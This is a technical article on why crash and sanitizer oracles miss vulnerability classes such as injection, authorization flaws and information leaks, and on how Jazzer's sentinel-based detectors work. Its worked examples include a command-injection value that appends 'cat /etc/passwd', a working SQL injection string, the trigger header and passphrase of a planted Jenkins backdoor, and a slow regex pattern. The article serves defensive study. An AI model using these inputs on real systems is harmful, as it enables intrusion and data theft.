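# Vulnerability classes invisible to sanitizer and crash oracles

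## How crash and sanitizer oracles work

A software vulnerability is a flaw that lets an attacker make a program do something its owners didn't intend, such as showing one customer's data to another or running commands on the server. The Common Weakness Enumeration (CWE) is the standard numbered catalogue of the types of mistakes that cause these flaws. Writing past the end of a buffer is CWE-787, reading past the end is CWE-125, and using memory after releasing it is CWE-416.

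Programs now do much of the searching for these mistakes by running software on inputs that might break it. After each run, a rule called the oracle determines whether the run exposed a bug. AI agents that hunt for bugs need an oracle as much as older tools do.

The simplest oracle is the crash. In the early 1990s Barton Miller and colleagues fed random strings to 88 programs and crashed more than 24% of them, as Kato, Shirai and colleagues (2026) recount in *Raise or Check?*. Miller's group called the technique fuzzing, and a tool that runs a program on very many generated inputs is still called a fuzzer. Modern ones are less random. Ding and Le Goues set out the usual loop in *An Empirical Study of OSS-Fuzz Bugs* (2021):

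1. The fuzzer picks an input from a pool of samples and alters it, for instance by flipping a bit.
2. It runs the program on the altered input.
3. If the run produces an error, the fuzzer reports the error and the input that caused it.
4. If the run produces no error but reaches code that no earlier input had reached, the input joins the pool for further alteration.

This loop does not check whether the program computed the right result. If a run triggers no error, the loop considers only which code the run reached, even if the output is wrong.

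A fuzzer supplies plain strings of bytes, but most code expects more structured input. A harness is a small program that converts the fuzzer's bytes into input the code under test accepts, then calls that code. The harness also makes a crash easy to check, because anyone can run it on the same input and see the same failure. An input or procedure that others can rerun to demonstrate a vulnerability is called a proof of vulnerability.

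OSS-Fuzz, a free service that Google has run for open-source projects since 2016, processes crashes automatically. When it finds a crash, it shrinks the input to a minimal reproducer. It then reruns that reproducer on older versions of the code, halving the range of versions each time, to narrow down the changes that introduced the bug. Later it reruns the reproducer on new versions to confirm the fix.

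### AddressSanitizer, step by step

Crashes alone are a poor guide to memory errors. A C or C++ program can compute almost any address and read or write there. If the address belongs to the program, the hardware does not raise a fault, and the program continues with wrong data. It may fail much later, somewhere else, or never. In the lecture slides *Automated Test-Case Generation*, Gurfinkel (2020) lists "do not crash" first among generic oracles and remarks that it is easy to check, but that a crash often comes too late or gives too little information.

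A sanitizer narrows this gap with instrumentation, extra code that checks a running program for a fixed kind of error and reports it. The best known is AddressSanitizer, or ASan, whose design Serebryany, Bruening and colleagues at Google described in *AddressSanitizer* (2012). A developer turns it on with a compiler option.

ASan divides the program's memory into groups of eight bytes and keeps one extra byte for each group, called the shadow byte, in **shadow memory**. A shadow byte of 0 means that the program may access all eight bytes, and a value *k* from 1 to 7 means that it may access only the first *k*. A negative value means that it may access none of them, and the specific value records why. To find the shadow byte for an address, ASan divides the address by eight and adds a fixed offset, which is fast enough to do at every access.

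ASan replaces the standard functions that allocate and free memory. Its versions surround each block with strips of forbidden, or "poisoned", memory called redzones, so a program that runs off the end of a block lands in one. The compiler adds similar strips around global variables and around variables on the stack, the region that holds a function's local data. When the program frees a block, ASan poisons the whole block and holds it in a quarantine queue for a while before reusing it. During that time, an access through a stale pointer to the block also hits poisoned memory.

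**The check.** Before each read or write in the compiled code, the compiler inserts a test. Let *k* be the shadow byte, *a* the address and *s* the number of bytes that the program wants, where *s* is smaller than eight. The access is bad if

*k* ≠ 0 and (*a* mod 8) + *s* > *k*.

A negative *k* always satisfies the second condition, so the same check catches accesses to redzones and freed memory. For a full eight-byte access, the test is only whether *k* is nonzero.

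If the test finds a bad access, ASan prints a report and ends the program with an error status. *AddressSanitizer*, the manual page from LLVM, the compiler project that maintains the tool, explains that ASan deliberately stops at the first error because corruption leaves the program in an inconsistent state and further reports could mislead. Aborting also makes ASan easy to combine with a fuzzer, which only has to detect that the process died. From here on, "crash oracle" means an oracle that counts only abnormal termination, including an abort forced by a sanitizer.

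AddressSanitizer slows programs moderately. Serebryany and colleagues measured an average slowdown of 73% on a standard set of benchmark programs, and LLVM now lists a twofold slowdown as typical. Valgrind, an older tool that needs no recompiling, slows programs about twentyfold, according to Trail of Bits' *Understanding AddressSanitizer* (2024).

ASan misses some memory errors. A write that overshoots its buffer by hundreds of bytes can skip the redzone and land in another valid block. ASan can also miss an access through a stale pointer if the program has since allocated and freed so much memory that the block has left quarantine. An overflow from one field of a structure into the next goes unreported because ASan puts no redzones between fields, since moving them apart would break programs that depend on their layout.

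Three related LLVM sanitizers check for other errors. *MemorySanitizer* checks for uses of uninitialised memory, such as branching on a value that was never set. *UndefinedBehaviorSanitizer* checks for operations that the C and C++ standards leave undefined, such as adding 1 to the largest value a signed integer can hold. *ThreadSanitizer* checks for data races, in which two threads use the same memory without coordination and at least one of them writes to it.

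Settings partly determine whether an error reported by these tools counts as a crash. MemorySanitizer, like ASan, stops the program at the first error. By default, UndefinedBehaviorSanitizer prints a message for most errors and lets the program continue, so an oracle that checks only how the process ended will miss those errors unless the developer configures the sanitizer to abort.

### Why the checks need no knowledge of the application

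These tools work without any information about what a program is for, because the rules they enforce come from the programming language and apply to every program. An out-of-bounds write, for example, is always wrong; as Wang, Görz and colleagues (2025) write in *Anota*, "a memory violation is never correct".

This is also why the reports are so reliable. Serebryany and colleagues state that ASan has no false positives, and LLVM advises anyone who thinks they have found one to look again. However, some of ASan's checks can report false positives when a developer has instrumented only part of a program. UndefinedBehaviorSanitizer also has optional checks for behaviour the language permits, so they can flag correct code. One of them reports unsigned integers that wrap around past zero. Programmers often rely on this wraparound, for example in a loop that counts down, so LLVM provides options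 to silence the most common harmless patterns.

Because the checks don't account for what the code is meant to do, they miss some memory-safety bugs too. Trail of Bits gives the example of a program with two arrays, A and B, which uses an index into A so large that the read lands inside B. The read is out of bounds for A, but ASan reports nothing because the program is allowed to use that address and ASan has no record of which array the programmer meant to read.

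### Two functions, one visible bug

Each of the two C functions below is missing one line, and a comment marks where it belongs. The first returns a character from a four-byte block of memory.

```c
char read_tag(int i)
{
    char *tag = malloc(4);
    char c;
    memcpy(tag, "Hey", 4);
    /* missing: reject i below 0 or above 3 */
    c = tag[i];
    free(tag);
    return c;
}
```

The second returns the balance of an account. Users 7 and 9 are customers, and each may see only their own accounts.

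```c
struct account { int owner; int balance; };
struct account accounts[3] = {{7, 120}, {7, 45}, {9, 8800}};

int read_balance(int user, int id)
{
    if (id < 0 || id > 2)
        return -1;
    /* missing: reject if accounts[id].owner != user */
    return accounts[id].balance;
}
```

Each function now gets a bad input. For `read_tag`, the input is position 4, which is one past the end because C counts from 0. In `read_balance`, user 7 asks for account 2, which belongs to user 9.

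| | `read_tag(4)` | `read_balance(7, 2)` |
|---|---|---|
| What goes wrong | Reads a fifth byte from a four-byte block | Gives user 7 the balance of user 9 |
| Shadow byte | 4 | 0 |
| ASan's test | 4 + 1 > 4, so the access is bad | *k* = 0, so the access is fine |
| End of the run with ASan | Error report and abort | Returns 8800 and continues |
| End of the run without ASan | Most likely returns a stray byte and continues | Returns 8800 and continues |

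Trail of Bits ran a program with nearly the same mistake as `read_tag`. ASan's report contained enough information for a developer to fix the bug. It identified a heap buffer overflow, described a one-byte read immediately after a four-byte region, and gave the source lines of both the read and the allocation.

No sanitizer reports anything when the missing check in `read_balance` exposes a stranger's balance. The function reads four bytes that lie well inside the array, that the program has initialised, and that no other thread is changing. More fuzzing would not help, because a fuzzer would run the faulty line almost at once, mark it as covered and move on. If the programmer had forgotten the bounds check instead, a request for account 3 would have run into a redzone and ASan would have aborted the program.

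The oracle lacks a policy, a statement of what the application should allow, and the code alone does not determine one. The same ten lines would be correct in a program for bank staff, where any clerk may look up any account. Wang and colleagues give authorization as a prominent example of a weakness for which nobody had proposed a sanitizer, because the tool would need to know which users may access what.

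### What these oracles have caught

Crash and sanitizer oracles have found many bugs of the kinds they can detect. Serebryany and colleagues reported more than 300 previously unknown bugs in the Chromium browser. According to Google's *OSS-Fuzz* page, the service had helped find and fix over 13,000 vulnerabilities and 50,000 bugs across 1,000 projects as of May 2025. Shirai, Nourry and colleagues (2026) report in *Does Programming Language Matter?* that it was fuzzing 1,311 projects by that September. In *From Finding to Fixing*, Kilian and Ingram (2026), who work on open-source security at Google, credit OSS-Fuzz with a "near-zero false positive rate" and contrast it with AI scanners that send maintainers many false reports. The main argument for requiring a crash is that doing so keeps false reports rare.

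However, a correct bug report does not always describe a serious vulnerability. The most detailed breakdown is by Ding and Le Goues, who sorted 23,907 bug reports by type of fault. OSS-Fuzz had filed these reports on 316 projects between May 2016 and October 2020.

| Type of fault | Share of reports | Main danger |
|---|---|---|
| Timeouts, exhausted memory, null pointers, stack overflows, memory leaks, aborts | 52% | The program stops or becomes unavailable |
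| Integer overflows, failed assertions, undefined shifts, division by zero | 23% | Unintended logic, sometimes exploitable |
| Out-of-bounds reads, uninitialised values, reads of released memory | 14% | Secrets leak from memory |
| Out-of-bounds writes | 2% | Corrupted data or an attacker's code running |

About half the reports in Ding and Le Goues's study concerned crashes, and only a small minority concerned the errors most useful to an attacker. They could match only 98 of the bugs to entries in CVE, the public register of individual vulnerabilities, and 80 of those were dangerous memory reads or writes. That count understates how many bugs were serious, because few people had filed entries even for memory corruption. The study also shows that reliable reproduction matters to developers. They had not fixed 86% of the bugs that did not reproduce reliably, compared with 12% of the rest,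 though some of the unreliable ones may not have been faults in the software.

The table is a poor guide to which flaws the projects contained. Its fault types are labels based on a crash, a timeout or a sanitizer report, and a flaw like the one in `read_balance` produces none of these, so it is not counted. Only assertions let these oracles use knowledge of the application. An assertion is a line in which a programmer writes a condition that must hold, and the program aborts if it doesn't. An assertion about account owners would have exposed the flaw in `read_balance`, but only if a programmer had thought to write one.

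Most of the bugs found this way are also in the languages these sanitizers were designed for. Shirai and colleagues analysed 61,444 OSS-Fuzz bugs and found that 85% came from projects written mainly in C or C++, which made up 61% of the projects. Those projects also had 73% of the builds, which explains part of the gap. Java projects accounted for under 4% of the bugs. Java itself stops ordinary code from running past the end of an array, and Jazzer, the main fuzzer for Java, adds detectors of a different kind.

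## Why some vulnerabilities produce no signal

A vulnerability is silent to an oracle when a run can cause all the harm the flaw allows without the oracle reporting anything. Silence depends on the oracle, so a claim of silence has to specify which one. For instance, the missing ownership check in `read_balance` is silent to AddressSanitizer but not to an assertion about account owners.

Bug finders also miss many flaws that can produce a signal. Sometimes no input reaches the faulty code, and finding the bug requires better inputs or another harness. Sometimes an input runs the faulty code without meeting the oracle's condition. *Assessing Claude Mythos Preview’s cybersecurity capabilities* (Carlini, Cheng and colleagues, 2026) describes a bug of this second kind that Anthropic's AI model found in FFmpeg, a widely used library for decoding video.

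FFmpeg's H.264 decoder splits each frame into slices and keeps a table of which slice each block of pixels belongs to. The entries are 16 bits wide, and 65,535 means that the block doesn't belong to a slice yet. Real videos have a handful of slices per frame, so the code that reads the table runs constantly without harm. In a frame with 65,536 slices, however, the last slice's number is also 65,535. The decoder then treats a nonexistent block as a neighbour and writes out of bounds. ASan detects the write, but fuzzers had missed the bug for 16 years, presumably because none of them built such a frame.

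A vulnerability can also produce no signal because the tester enabled the wrong sanitizer. The AI Cyber Challenge (AIxCC) was a US government contest for systems that find and fix vulnerabilities without human help, and its final included a signed integer overflow in the video decoder dav1d. Zhang, Park and colleagues (2026) report in *SoK* that UndefinedBehaviorSanitizer was needed to detect this overflow and that ASan could not detect it. Several of the seven finalists had included the right sanitizer, yet only the Trail of Bits team handled the bug correctly. The overflow was silent to ASan by the definition above, but a standard tool reports it, so the remedy is correct configuration and no new check is needed.

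From here on, "silent" with no oracle named means silent to a crash oracle under every one of the four LLVM sanitizers.

### The oracle problem

Software testing in general has the same difficulty. Generating inputs is easier to automate than deciding whether the program handled them correctly, and the second task is called the oracle problem. *The Oracle Problem in Software Testing* (Barr, Harman and colleagues, 2015) defines an oracle as a function *D* that accepts or rejects a program's response to its inputs, and compares it with an ideal oracle *G* that always gives the right answer.

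- *D* is **sound** if *D*(*a*) ⇒ *G*(*a*), so that every behaviour it accepts really is acceptable.
- *D* is **complete** if *G*(*a*) ⇒ *D*(*a*), so that it accepts every acceptable behaviour.

A crash oracle accepts every run that ends normally. Correct programs rarely crash, so the oracle is close to complete and produces few false reports. But it is far from sound, because it also accepts runs that trigger silent vulnerabilities. For example, the call `read_balance(7, 2)` ends normally, but *G* would reject it. Barr and colleagues add that an oracle cannot in general be both sound and complete.

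Barr and colleagues class crash detection as an implicit oracle, which relies on general rules and needs no specification. Fuzzing works because such rules hold for nearly all inputs, including ones nobody has examined. A specification more often relates particular inputs to particular outputs, and somebody has to write it. Of the 694 publications from 1978 to 2012 that Barr and colleagues collected, 76 dealt with implicit oracles, 317 with oracles based on a formal specification, and 245 with oracles derived from other material, such as documentation or an older version of the program.

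### Four causes of silence

A crash oracle can accept a harmful run for any of four reasons, and one flaw may involve several of them.

| Cause | Example | What the oracle lacks |
|---|---|---|
| The harm happens in another interpreter | Text from a user becomes a shell command | A check on what the shell will do with the text |
| The wrong depends on the application's policy | `read_balance` | A statement of who may see what |
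| The wrong shows only when someone compares runs | Output that varies with a secret | A second run |
| The signal is physical | A password check that takes longer for better guesses | A measurement of time, power or heat |

### Harm in another interpreter

Suppose a web page lets users test a network connection. The program behind it appends the address a user types to the text `ping -c 1 ` and passes the result to the shell, which runs text as commands. A user who types `192.0.2.1; cat /etc/passwd` makes the shell run `ping` and then print a system file.

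The web program does nothing irregular. It joins two strings in a large enough buffer and makes a call that the operating system permits. The semicolon is special only to the shell, a separate program that lacks the sanitizer's instrumentation and also works as designed. SQL injection follows the same pattern, with a database in place of the shell. In cross-site scripting, the interpreter is another visitor's browser.

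Carlini and colleagues describe SQL injection and cross-site scripting as "in the same spirit as memory corruption", and skip them for that reason. The comparison has considerable merit. In a FreeBSD bug they recount, a server has room for 96 bytes from a network packet but accepts up to 400, and the excess overwrites data that determines which code the kernel runs next. As in the shell example, the machine ends up following an attacker's data as instructions. The rule against this also looks nearly universal, since very few applications mean to let a stranger add a command. A single run is enough to show that the rule was violated.

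Unlike a buffer overflow, an injected semicolon triggers no ASan report. Detecting injection also requires knowing the trust boundary, the line between input an attacker may control and input the program may trust. A database administrator's console, for example, is meant to run whatever SQL its user types. Memory-safety checks don't need to know this boundary, because no program is meant to write past the end of its buffers.

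Injection allows a similar sort of check to memory corruption, but existing sanitizers don't report it. It is probably the easiest of the silent classes to give an oracle, because the obvious place for the check is the sink, a call that does something security-sensitive, such as running a command or opening a file.

### A policy the code does not contain

Carlini and colleagues define logic bugs as gaps between what the code does and what its specification or security model requires. These bugs have no obvious location, and the program never takes an easily recognised forbidden action, so a fuzzer has nothing to flag. The researchers call ASan "a perfect crash oracle" and had found no false positives in FFmpeg, but they could not confirm the model's reports of logic bugs with the same near-perfect reliability.

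A little theory shows what exactly is missing. A trace is the sequence of states that a program goes through in one run. A trace property *P* is a set of traces, the ones that some rule allows. If *T* is the set of all traces a system can produce, the system obeys the rule when

*T* ⊆ *P*.

One trace outside *P* is enough to show that the system breaks the rule. ASan imperfectly enforces a property of this kind, where *P* is the set of traces in which every memory access is valid.

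Access control is also a trace property, as Clarkson and Schneider (2009) show in *Hyperproperties*. They use a table listing each user's rights over each object. A trace belongs to *P* if, just before each step, the table grants the rights that the step's operation needs. The call `read_balance(7, 2)` breaks this rule in a single run, when user 7 receives an account belonging to user 9.

An authorization violation is therefore as definite as a buffer overflow, and it occurs at an identifiable step. It produces no signal because the oracle usually lacks the table of rights needed to detect it, not because it is hard to observe.

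### A difference between runs

For leaks of secret information, a written policy may still not be enough. In an example from Clarkson and Schneider, one system holds a secret bit and outputs 0, 1 or the secret bit, chosen at random. It can output 0 or 1 whatever the secret is, so it obeys the rule that a system's possible outputs must not depend on the secret. Another system always outputs the secret bit, which breaks the rule.

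Yet every run of the leaky system is also a possible run of the safe one. If the rule were a trace property *P*, all the safe system's traces would satisfy *P*, and therefore so would all the leaky system's traces. So no rule about individual runs can accept the safe system and reject the leaky one.

Clarkson and Schneider therefore define a **hyperproperty** as a set *H* of sets of traces. Each member of *H* is the complete behaviour of one permitted system, and a system obeys the rule when

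*T* ∈ *H*.

The change from ⊆ to ∈ means that the rule applies to the system's whole set of runs, not to each run separately. Trace properties are a special case of hyperproperties. As *A Temporal Logic of Security* (2013) notes, the hyperproperty that matches a trace property *P* is the set of all subsets of *P*. But all the information-flow policies that Clarkson and Schneider examined required hyperproperties. Finkbeiner (2025), in *Logics and Algorithms for Hyperproperties*, likewise holds that individual executions are not enough to judge information-flow requirements.

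Testers can check some requirements, called two-run properties, only by comparing two or more executions. The best known is noninterference, which roughly requires that secret inputs do not affect what an outsider observes. A deterministic program violates it if two runs with the same public inputs but different secrets produce different public outputs, even though each run may look normal on its own.

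A crash oracle can still detect such flaws. Clarkson and Schneider prove that if *k* runs are always enough to expose a violation, the rule is equivalent to a trace property of a larger system made of *k* copies of the original. A harness could therefore run the code twice with different secrets and abort if the public outputs differ. This also requires a policy, because the tester must first say which inputs are secret and which outputs are public. Random choices complicate the comparison because they can make a program's outputs differ even when it leaks nothing.

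For some rules, no fixed number of runs is always enough to prove a violation. Clarkson and Schneider describe a system that splits a secret into *k* shares and outputs one share per run. An attacker needs all *k* shares to recover the secret, so if it is split into 50 shares, no set of 49 runs can prove a leak.

An ordinary crash oracle can detect a bug that takes two runs to trigger if it runs the input more than once. In the AIxCC final, one flaw in systemd, which manages services on Linux, caused a crash only on the second execution. The organisers reran each input 100 times by default and saw the crash, while contest systems that checked an input once threw away valid proofs. The second run crashes by itself, so detecting the bug doesn't require comparing the two runs.

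### A physical signal

The usual fuzzing loop records which code ran and how the process ended. A program also takes time, draws power and gives off heat. Barr and colleagues count all of these as observations an oracle may use, but a crash oracle doesn't use them.

Some flaws show only in how long a program takes to run. A password check that stops at the first wrong character takes slightly longer when the guess begins correctly. It returns the same "no" to every wrong guess, so a tester has to compare the durations of two runs instead of their outputs. This flaw combines two of the causes of a missing signal, because the output doesn't reveal it and one duration means little without another for comparison.

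### Three hard cases

Heartbleed, disclosed in 2014, was a flaw in OpenSSL, a library that encrypts much of the web's traffic. Either side of a connection could send a short "heartbeat" message, whose contents the other side would send back. OpenSSL did not check the length stated in the message against its real length. An attacker could send a byte or so, state a length of about 64 kilobytes and receive that much of the server's memory, sometimes including passwords or private keys.

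ASan can detect Heartbleed without comparing runs because the bug leaks secrets by reading past the end of a buffer. Without a sanitizer, the server normally sent the bytes and kept running, so a plain crash oracle had no crash to detect. ASan reported the bug only when the false length was large enough to read past the buffer. OpenSSL held incoming messages in a buffer much larger than a typical heartbeat, so a moderately false length returned leftovers from earlier messages without leaving the buffer.

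Carlini and colleagues describe a flaw that the model found in the Linux kernel. The kernel places its code and data at random addresses so that an attacker who can write to kernel memory doesn't know where to aim. One part of the kernel deliberately gives one of its addresses to ordinary programs, which defeats the protection. As with Heartbleed, though on a smaller scale, secret data reaches someone who should not have it. But here the code does what its developer intended, so there is no out-of-bounds read for a sanitizer to detect.

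The oracle misses this leak because disclosing a kernel address is wrong only under a policy that keeps those addresses secret. Given that policy, a tester could search the kernel's output for values that look like kernel addresses. Comparing two boots with different random layouts might also expose the leak. Whether an oracle reports an information leak thus depends on how the information got out, which the label "information leak" doesn't specify.

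A slow regular expression can allow a denial of service, because a few dozen characters of input can keep a server busy for a long time. A regular expression is a pattern for matching text, and many engines match by trying one possibility after another. The pattern `^(a+)+$` accepts any string made up only of the letter *a*, which it treats as one or more groups. There are 2^(*n*−1) ways to divide *n* letters into groups. If the text is 30 letters *a* followed by an exclamation mark, no division can succeed, and a simple engine tries all 536,870,912 before reporting no match.

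The program does not crash and its eventual answer is correct, so the only signal is how long it takes. No finite run can show that the program violates the requirement that every request eventually gets a response, because the response might still come. Testers therefore replace that requirement with a time limit, such as 25 seconds. By Clarkson and Schneider's theory, a single run is enough to show that a program violates a maximum response time set for each run. Fuzzers commonly have such a limit, which is why OSS-Fuzz reports include timeouts.

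The fuzzer's time limit determines which slow inputs it reports. With 20 letters instead of 30, the engine tries 524,288 ways to divide the string and probably finishes well within any limit a fuzzer would use, although an attacker could send thousands of such requests.

Timeouts are also poor signals when they do occur. AIxCC included a slow regular expression in poi, a Java library for office documents. Contest systems could find it where ordinary fuzzing did not, but none repaired it. Zhang and colleagues explain that timeouts give little information about where the fault lies and look nearly identical to one another. In one harness for the PDF library pdfbox, tools merged distinct timeout bugs into one, and a shallow timeout kept recurring and prevented the tools from reaching deeper bugs.

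### Security oracles in published systems

Researchers in automated testing have put much more work into reaching code than into judging what the code does. *Adaptive and AI-Augmented Security Testing* (Wienczkowski, 2026) reviews 55 peer-reviewed studies and compares twelve systems that adapt to feedback or combine several methods. Ten used code coverage as their main feedback. Only two had an oracle specific to security: SAGE, a Microsoft tool that solves for inputs leading down new branches, and Securify, which checks Ethereum smart contracts against patterns of known vulnerabilities.

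The exact count may be off, because Wienczkowski did the classification alone and the survey's own comparison table lists Securify as having no feedback at all, which makes its place among the twelve puzzling. The two exceptions, SAGE and Securify, also don't help much with silent vulnerabilities in running programs. By Wienczkowski's account, SAGE relies on assertion failures and ASan's reports of memory corruption, so it has a crash oracle. Securify examines a contract's code in a single pass, without evaluating any executions.

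On this evidence, "two of twelve" if anything overstates how well the research systems do. It is less informative about the tools developers use, because the survey left preprints and tool documentation out of its main sample. Jazzer, for example, has checks for several kinds of injection.

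## How Jazzer's injection detectors work

A Java program can make the same mistake as the web page that runs `ping`, and the run looks just as normal. When a Java program starts another program, the call returns an object that represents the new process, whether or not an attacker chose the program.

Jazzer is an open-source fuzzer from Code Intelligence for the Java virtual machine (JVM), which executes compiled Java code. Without special detectors, it reports runs that never finish and exceptions (Java's error signals) that no code catches. An uncaught exception is roughly the Java counterpart of a crash. A successful injection doesn't cause an endless run or an uncaught exception.

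Jazzer therefore adds injection detectors, which are attached to sinks and report when input controls the call in a forbidden way. Meumertzheim (2022), one of Jazzer's developers, argued in his talk *Fuzzing Java with Jazzer* that fuzzers already explore programs well, so they only need a way to detect a vulnerability when it happens. He cited ASan as the precedent.

### From a method call to a finding

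Jazzer includes an agent that runs inside the JVM and rewrites classes as the JVM loads them, so it does not need the program's source code. According to Code Intelligence's *Advanced options*, the agent inserts markers that record which code ran. It also inserts hooks, which are pieces of code that run before, after or instead of a method call and can read its arguments.

The command-injection detector hooks `ProcessImpl.start`, the internal method through which Java starts a program. Jazzer normally leaves Java's own library classes unchanged, so the detector's code has to list `ProcessBuilder`, the library class that calls `ProcessImpl.start`, as a class to rewrite.

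**The condition.** In simplified form, the hook does this:

```text
before ProcessImpl.start(command):
    name = first element of command
    if name is "jazze":
        report "OS Command Injection"
    else:
        pass name and "jazze" to the fuzzing engine
```

The word `jazze` is a sentinel, a harmless marker that the detector looks for as a sign of attacker control. Hardly any software would otherwise start a program called `jazze`, so if that name reaches the sink, it almost certainly came from the fuzzer's input, and the detector doesn't have to trace how it got there. The finding is valid only if an attacker could control what the harness passes in, so a badly designed harness can cause a false finding.

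A blind guess at five particular bytes has about one chance in 1.1 trillion of being right. The last line of the hook improves those odds by passing both strings to libFuzzer, the LLVM fuzzing engine that generates Jazzer's inputs, as if the program itself had compared them. libFuzzer keeps a table of recently compared values and tries inserting them into later inputs. Each entry holds at most 64 bytes, so Code Intelligence kept even the detectors' more elaborate targets within that length.

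An option called value profile counts progress on a comparison as new coverage, so the fuzzer can keep an input that matches only part of the sentinel. Meumertzheim notes that this slows fuzzing but can uncover code the fuzzer would not otherwise reach.

Team Atlanta, which won AIxCC, saw the importance of this feedback when it replaced libFuzzer with a newer engine, LibAFL. According to the team's *Jazzer+LibAFL*, the new engine sometimes failed on simple harnesses because its comparison hooks did not measure how close two values were. Even with good feedback, inserting `jazze` into the raw input may not put `jazze` in the command if the program decodes or rearranges its input before the sink.

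When the condition holds, the hook creates an exception describing the vulnerability and passes it to Jazzer. Jazzer records it separately, so the finding isn't lost if the program catches the exception. The user sees a Java error with a stack trace, and Jazzer saves the input so it can be rerun.

An ordinary crash reaches the fuzzing engine as a signal from the operating system. Jazzer instead notifies the engine through a function called a death callback, which Team Atlanta had to add to LibAFL. *ATLANTIS* (2025), the team's description of its contest system, says that without such changes LibAFL would have missed Java findings that do not appear as traditional crashes. The callback lets the rest of the fuzzing system treat an injection like a buffer overflow that ASan caught.

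### A planted command injection in Jenkins

For its semifinal, AIxCC used a version of Jenkins, a server that builds and tests software, with a planted backdoor. Fleischer, Zhang and colleagues (2026), in *Contextualizing Sink Knowledge for Java Vulnerability Discovery*, reproduce the code. A web request has to pass three checks before it can start a program:

1. It must carry a header called `x-evil-backdoor`.
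2. The header's value must have the same SHA-256 hash as the phrase "breakin the law". A hash is a fixed-length fingerprint that nobody can feasibly reverse, so in practice the value must be the phrase itself.
3. The command must not be blank.

The program then puts the command into an array as its only element, gives the array to `ProcessBuilder` and calls `start`.

The hash check is the hardest for a fuzzer to pass. Even if the fuzzer learns which hash the program expects, it can't recover the phrase from it. A person or a language model can copy the phrase from the source code.

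Suppose that a request passes all three checks. The outcome now depends on the command.

| Command | Without the detector | With the detector |
|---|---|---|
| `id` | The server runs `id`, which prints the current user's identity, and continues | The same, but the engine also receives `id` and `jazze` as a comparison |
| `nosuchprogram` | Java throws an exception, and the code catches it | The same, but the engine also receives the comparison |
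| `jazze` | Java throws an exception, and the code catches it | Jazzer reports command injection before Java tries to start anything |

All three commands reach the sink, but Jazzer reports a bug only for `jazze`, a sentinel that stands for any program an attacker might name. Running `jazze` on a real server would fail because no such program exists. Jazzer doesn't report `id`, even though that command would work on a real server.

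The match must be exact. Fleischer and colleagues write in one place that the command must begin with "jazze", but their annotated code tests for equality, and Jazzer's source also steers the fuzzer towards equality. DARPA, the US defence research agency that ran AIxCC, chose Jazzer as the baseline for the Java challenges, so contest systems had to meet such conditions exactly. Team Atlanta gives the example of a program that loads whatever class a request names. To get credit, the team's language model had to supply the class name `jaz.Zer`, and `jaz.Zero` or `jaz.zer` would fail.

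Fleischer and colleagues report that in the Jenkins case, Jazzer's guidance is enough to find the sentinel once an input reaches the sink. In other cases it is often not enough, and Jazzer missed most of the vulnerabilities in their benchmark.

### What each detector tests

Jazzer had seven injection detectors when Meumertzheim gave his talk in April 2022, and developers have since added more. Several detectors use `jaz.Zer`, a honeypot class that ordinary programs have no reason to use. If a program loads the class or runs its code, the fuzzer's input has probably determined what the program executes.

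Most of the conditions below come from source code that Code Intelligence published around 2023.

| Detector | Call it checks | Condition for a report |
|---|---|---|
| Command injection | Starting a program | The program's name is `jazze` |
| Reflection | Loading a class or native library by name | The program loads `jaz.Zer`, or the library's name equals a sentinel |
| Deserialization | Rebuilding an object from stored bytes | The bytes produce a `jaz.Zer` object |
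| Expression-language injection | Evaluating a small expression, such as one in a message template | The expression runs a method of `jaz.Zer` |
| Script injection | Running a script inside the JVM | The script contains the text `"jaz"+"zer"` |
| JNDI lookup | Looking up an object by name, possibly on another server | The name begins with `ldap://g.co/` or `rmi://g.co/` |
| SQL injection | Sending a text query to a database | A separate parser rejects the query, and the database call throws one of five listed exceptions |
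| LDAP injection | Searching a directory, such as a staff directory | The search fails with a naming error, which includes an invalid filter |
| XPath injection | Querying an XML document | The query fails with an error that indicates broken syntax |
| Regular-expression injection | Compiling a pattern | The pattern has a syntax error, or it contains a sentinel while a costly Unicode option is on |
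| Server-side request forgery | Opening a network connection | The developer has not allowed that host and port |
| Path traversal | Opening a file | In a 2021 draft, the file lies outside a list of allowed paths |
| Unsafe array access | Using an array through `sun.misc.Unsafe`, which skips Java's usual checks | The access is invalid for that array |

The path-traversal condition comes from *A draft of a path traversal sanitizer for Jazzer*. Developers can configure the released detector, according to Socket's copy of the version 0.30.0 documentation (*com.code-intelligence:jazzer*, February 2026).

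Exact sentinels give strong evidence that input controls the value, but they are narrow. The command detector checks only the first element of the command. In the `ping` example, a Java version of the web page would run the shell, `sh`, with the text containing the user's address as an argument. The first element is always `sh`, so the detector would miss an injected semicolon. Meumertzheim said in 2022 that the detector did not yet consider arguments, and the later source code still compared only the first element.

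**Honeypot classes** provide some of the most direct evidence, because the program creates an object or runs code that the input selected. The script detector is less strict. It searches the script's text before anything runs, so it also reports a sentinel inside a comment, which the script engine would ignore.

**Syntax errors.** The SQL, LDAP and XPath detectors mostly look for input that breaks a query. Suppose that a program finds a user by placing a name between two quotation marks:

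```sql
SELECT * FROM users WHERE name = '...'
```

If the input is a single quotation mark, the query contains an unfinished string. The parser rejects the query, the database throws an exception, and Jazzer reports SQL injection. The input `' OR '1'='1` is a real attack that produces a valid query and returns every user, but Jazzer doesn't report it because the parser accepts the query and the database throws no exception.

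The SQL detector is thus more likely to flag an injection attempt that produces a broken query than a working exploit. This suits a fuzzer, which produces broken queries far more often than valid ones, and a broken query is good evidence that the program failed to escape its input. It suits an AI agent less well, because an agent may write a working exploit without first producing a broken query.

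The SQL detector also depends on the database used in the test. It looks for the exception's exact class name in a list, which lacked the class thrown by PostgreSQL's standard Java driver. According to comments in the source code, the detector can produce some false positives because no single parser handles every SQL dialect. An unusual but correct query that fails because a table is missing can look like an injection.

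**Allowed destinations.** Server-side request forgery lets an attacker make a server send requests to destinations the attacker chooses, often inside a private network. Jazzer's detector for this flaw checks connections against a rule instead of looking for a sentinel. The default rule permits no connections, so the detector reports any that the program tries to make, even to a hard-coded address. Developers can supply their own rule listing the expected hosts, which is a small policy of the kind that a crash oracle lacks.

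Jazzer also gives each finding a severity, which mostly reflects the possible harm rather than the strength of the evidence. It rates an LDAP search that fails with a naming error as critical, the same as a command named `jazze`. An unapproved network connection is medium, and a broken regular expression is low.

**Unsafe array access.** This check concerns memory safety rather than injection. Marcono1234 (2025) proposed it in *Add Unsafe array access sanitizer* after several Java libraries had used `Unsafe` for speed and introduced security flaws. The mailing-list post *On the unsafety of sun.misc.Unsafe* (2025) reports that by September, Jazzer 0.25.0 could detect unsafe array accesses.

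Unlike ASan, the detector can compare the access with the length of the intended array, because the call to `Unsafe` specifies that array. Marcono1234 still expects fuzzing to miss some of these bugs, because they appear only after a program has processed several megabytes of data.

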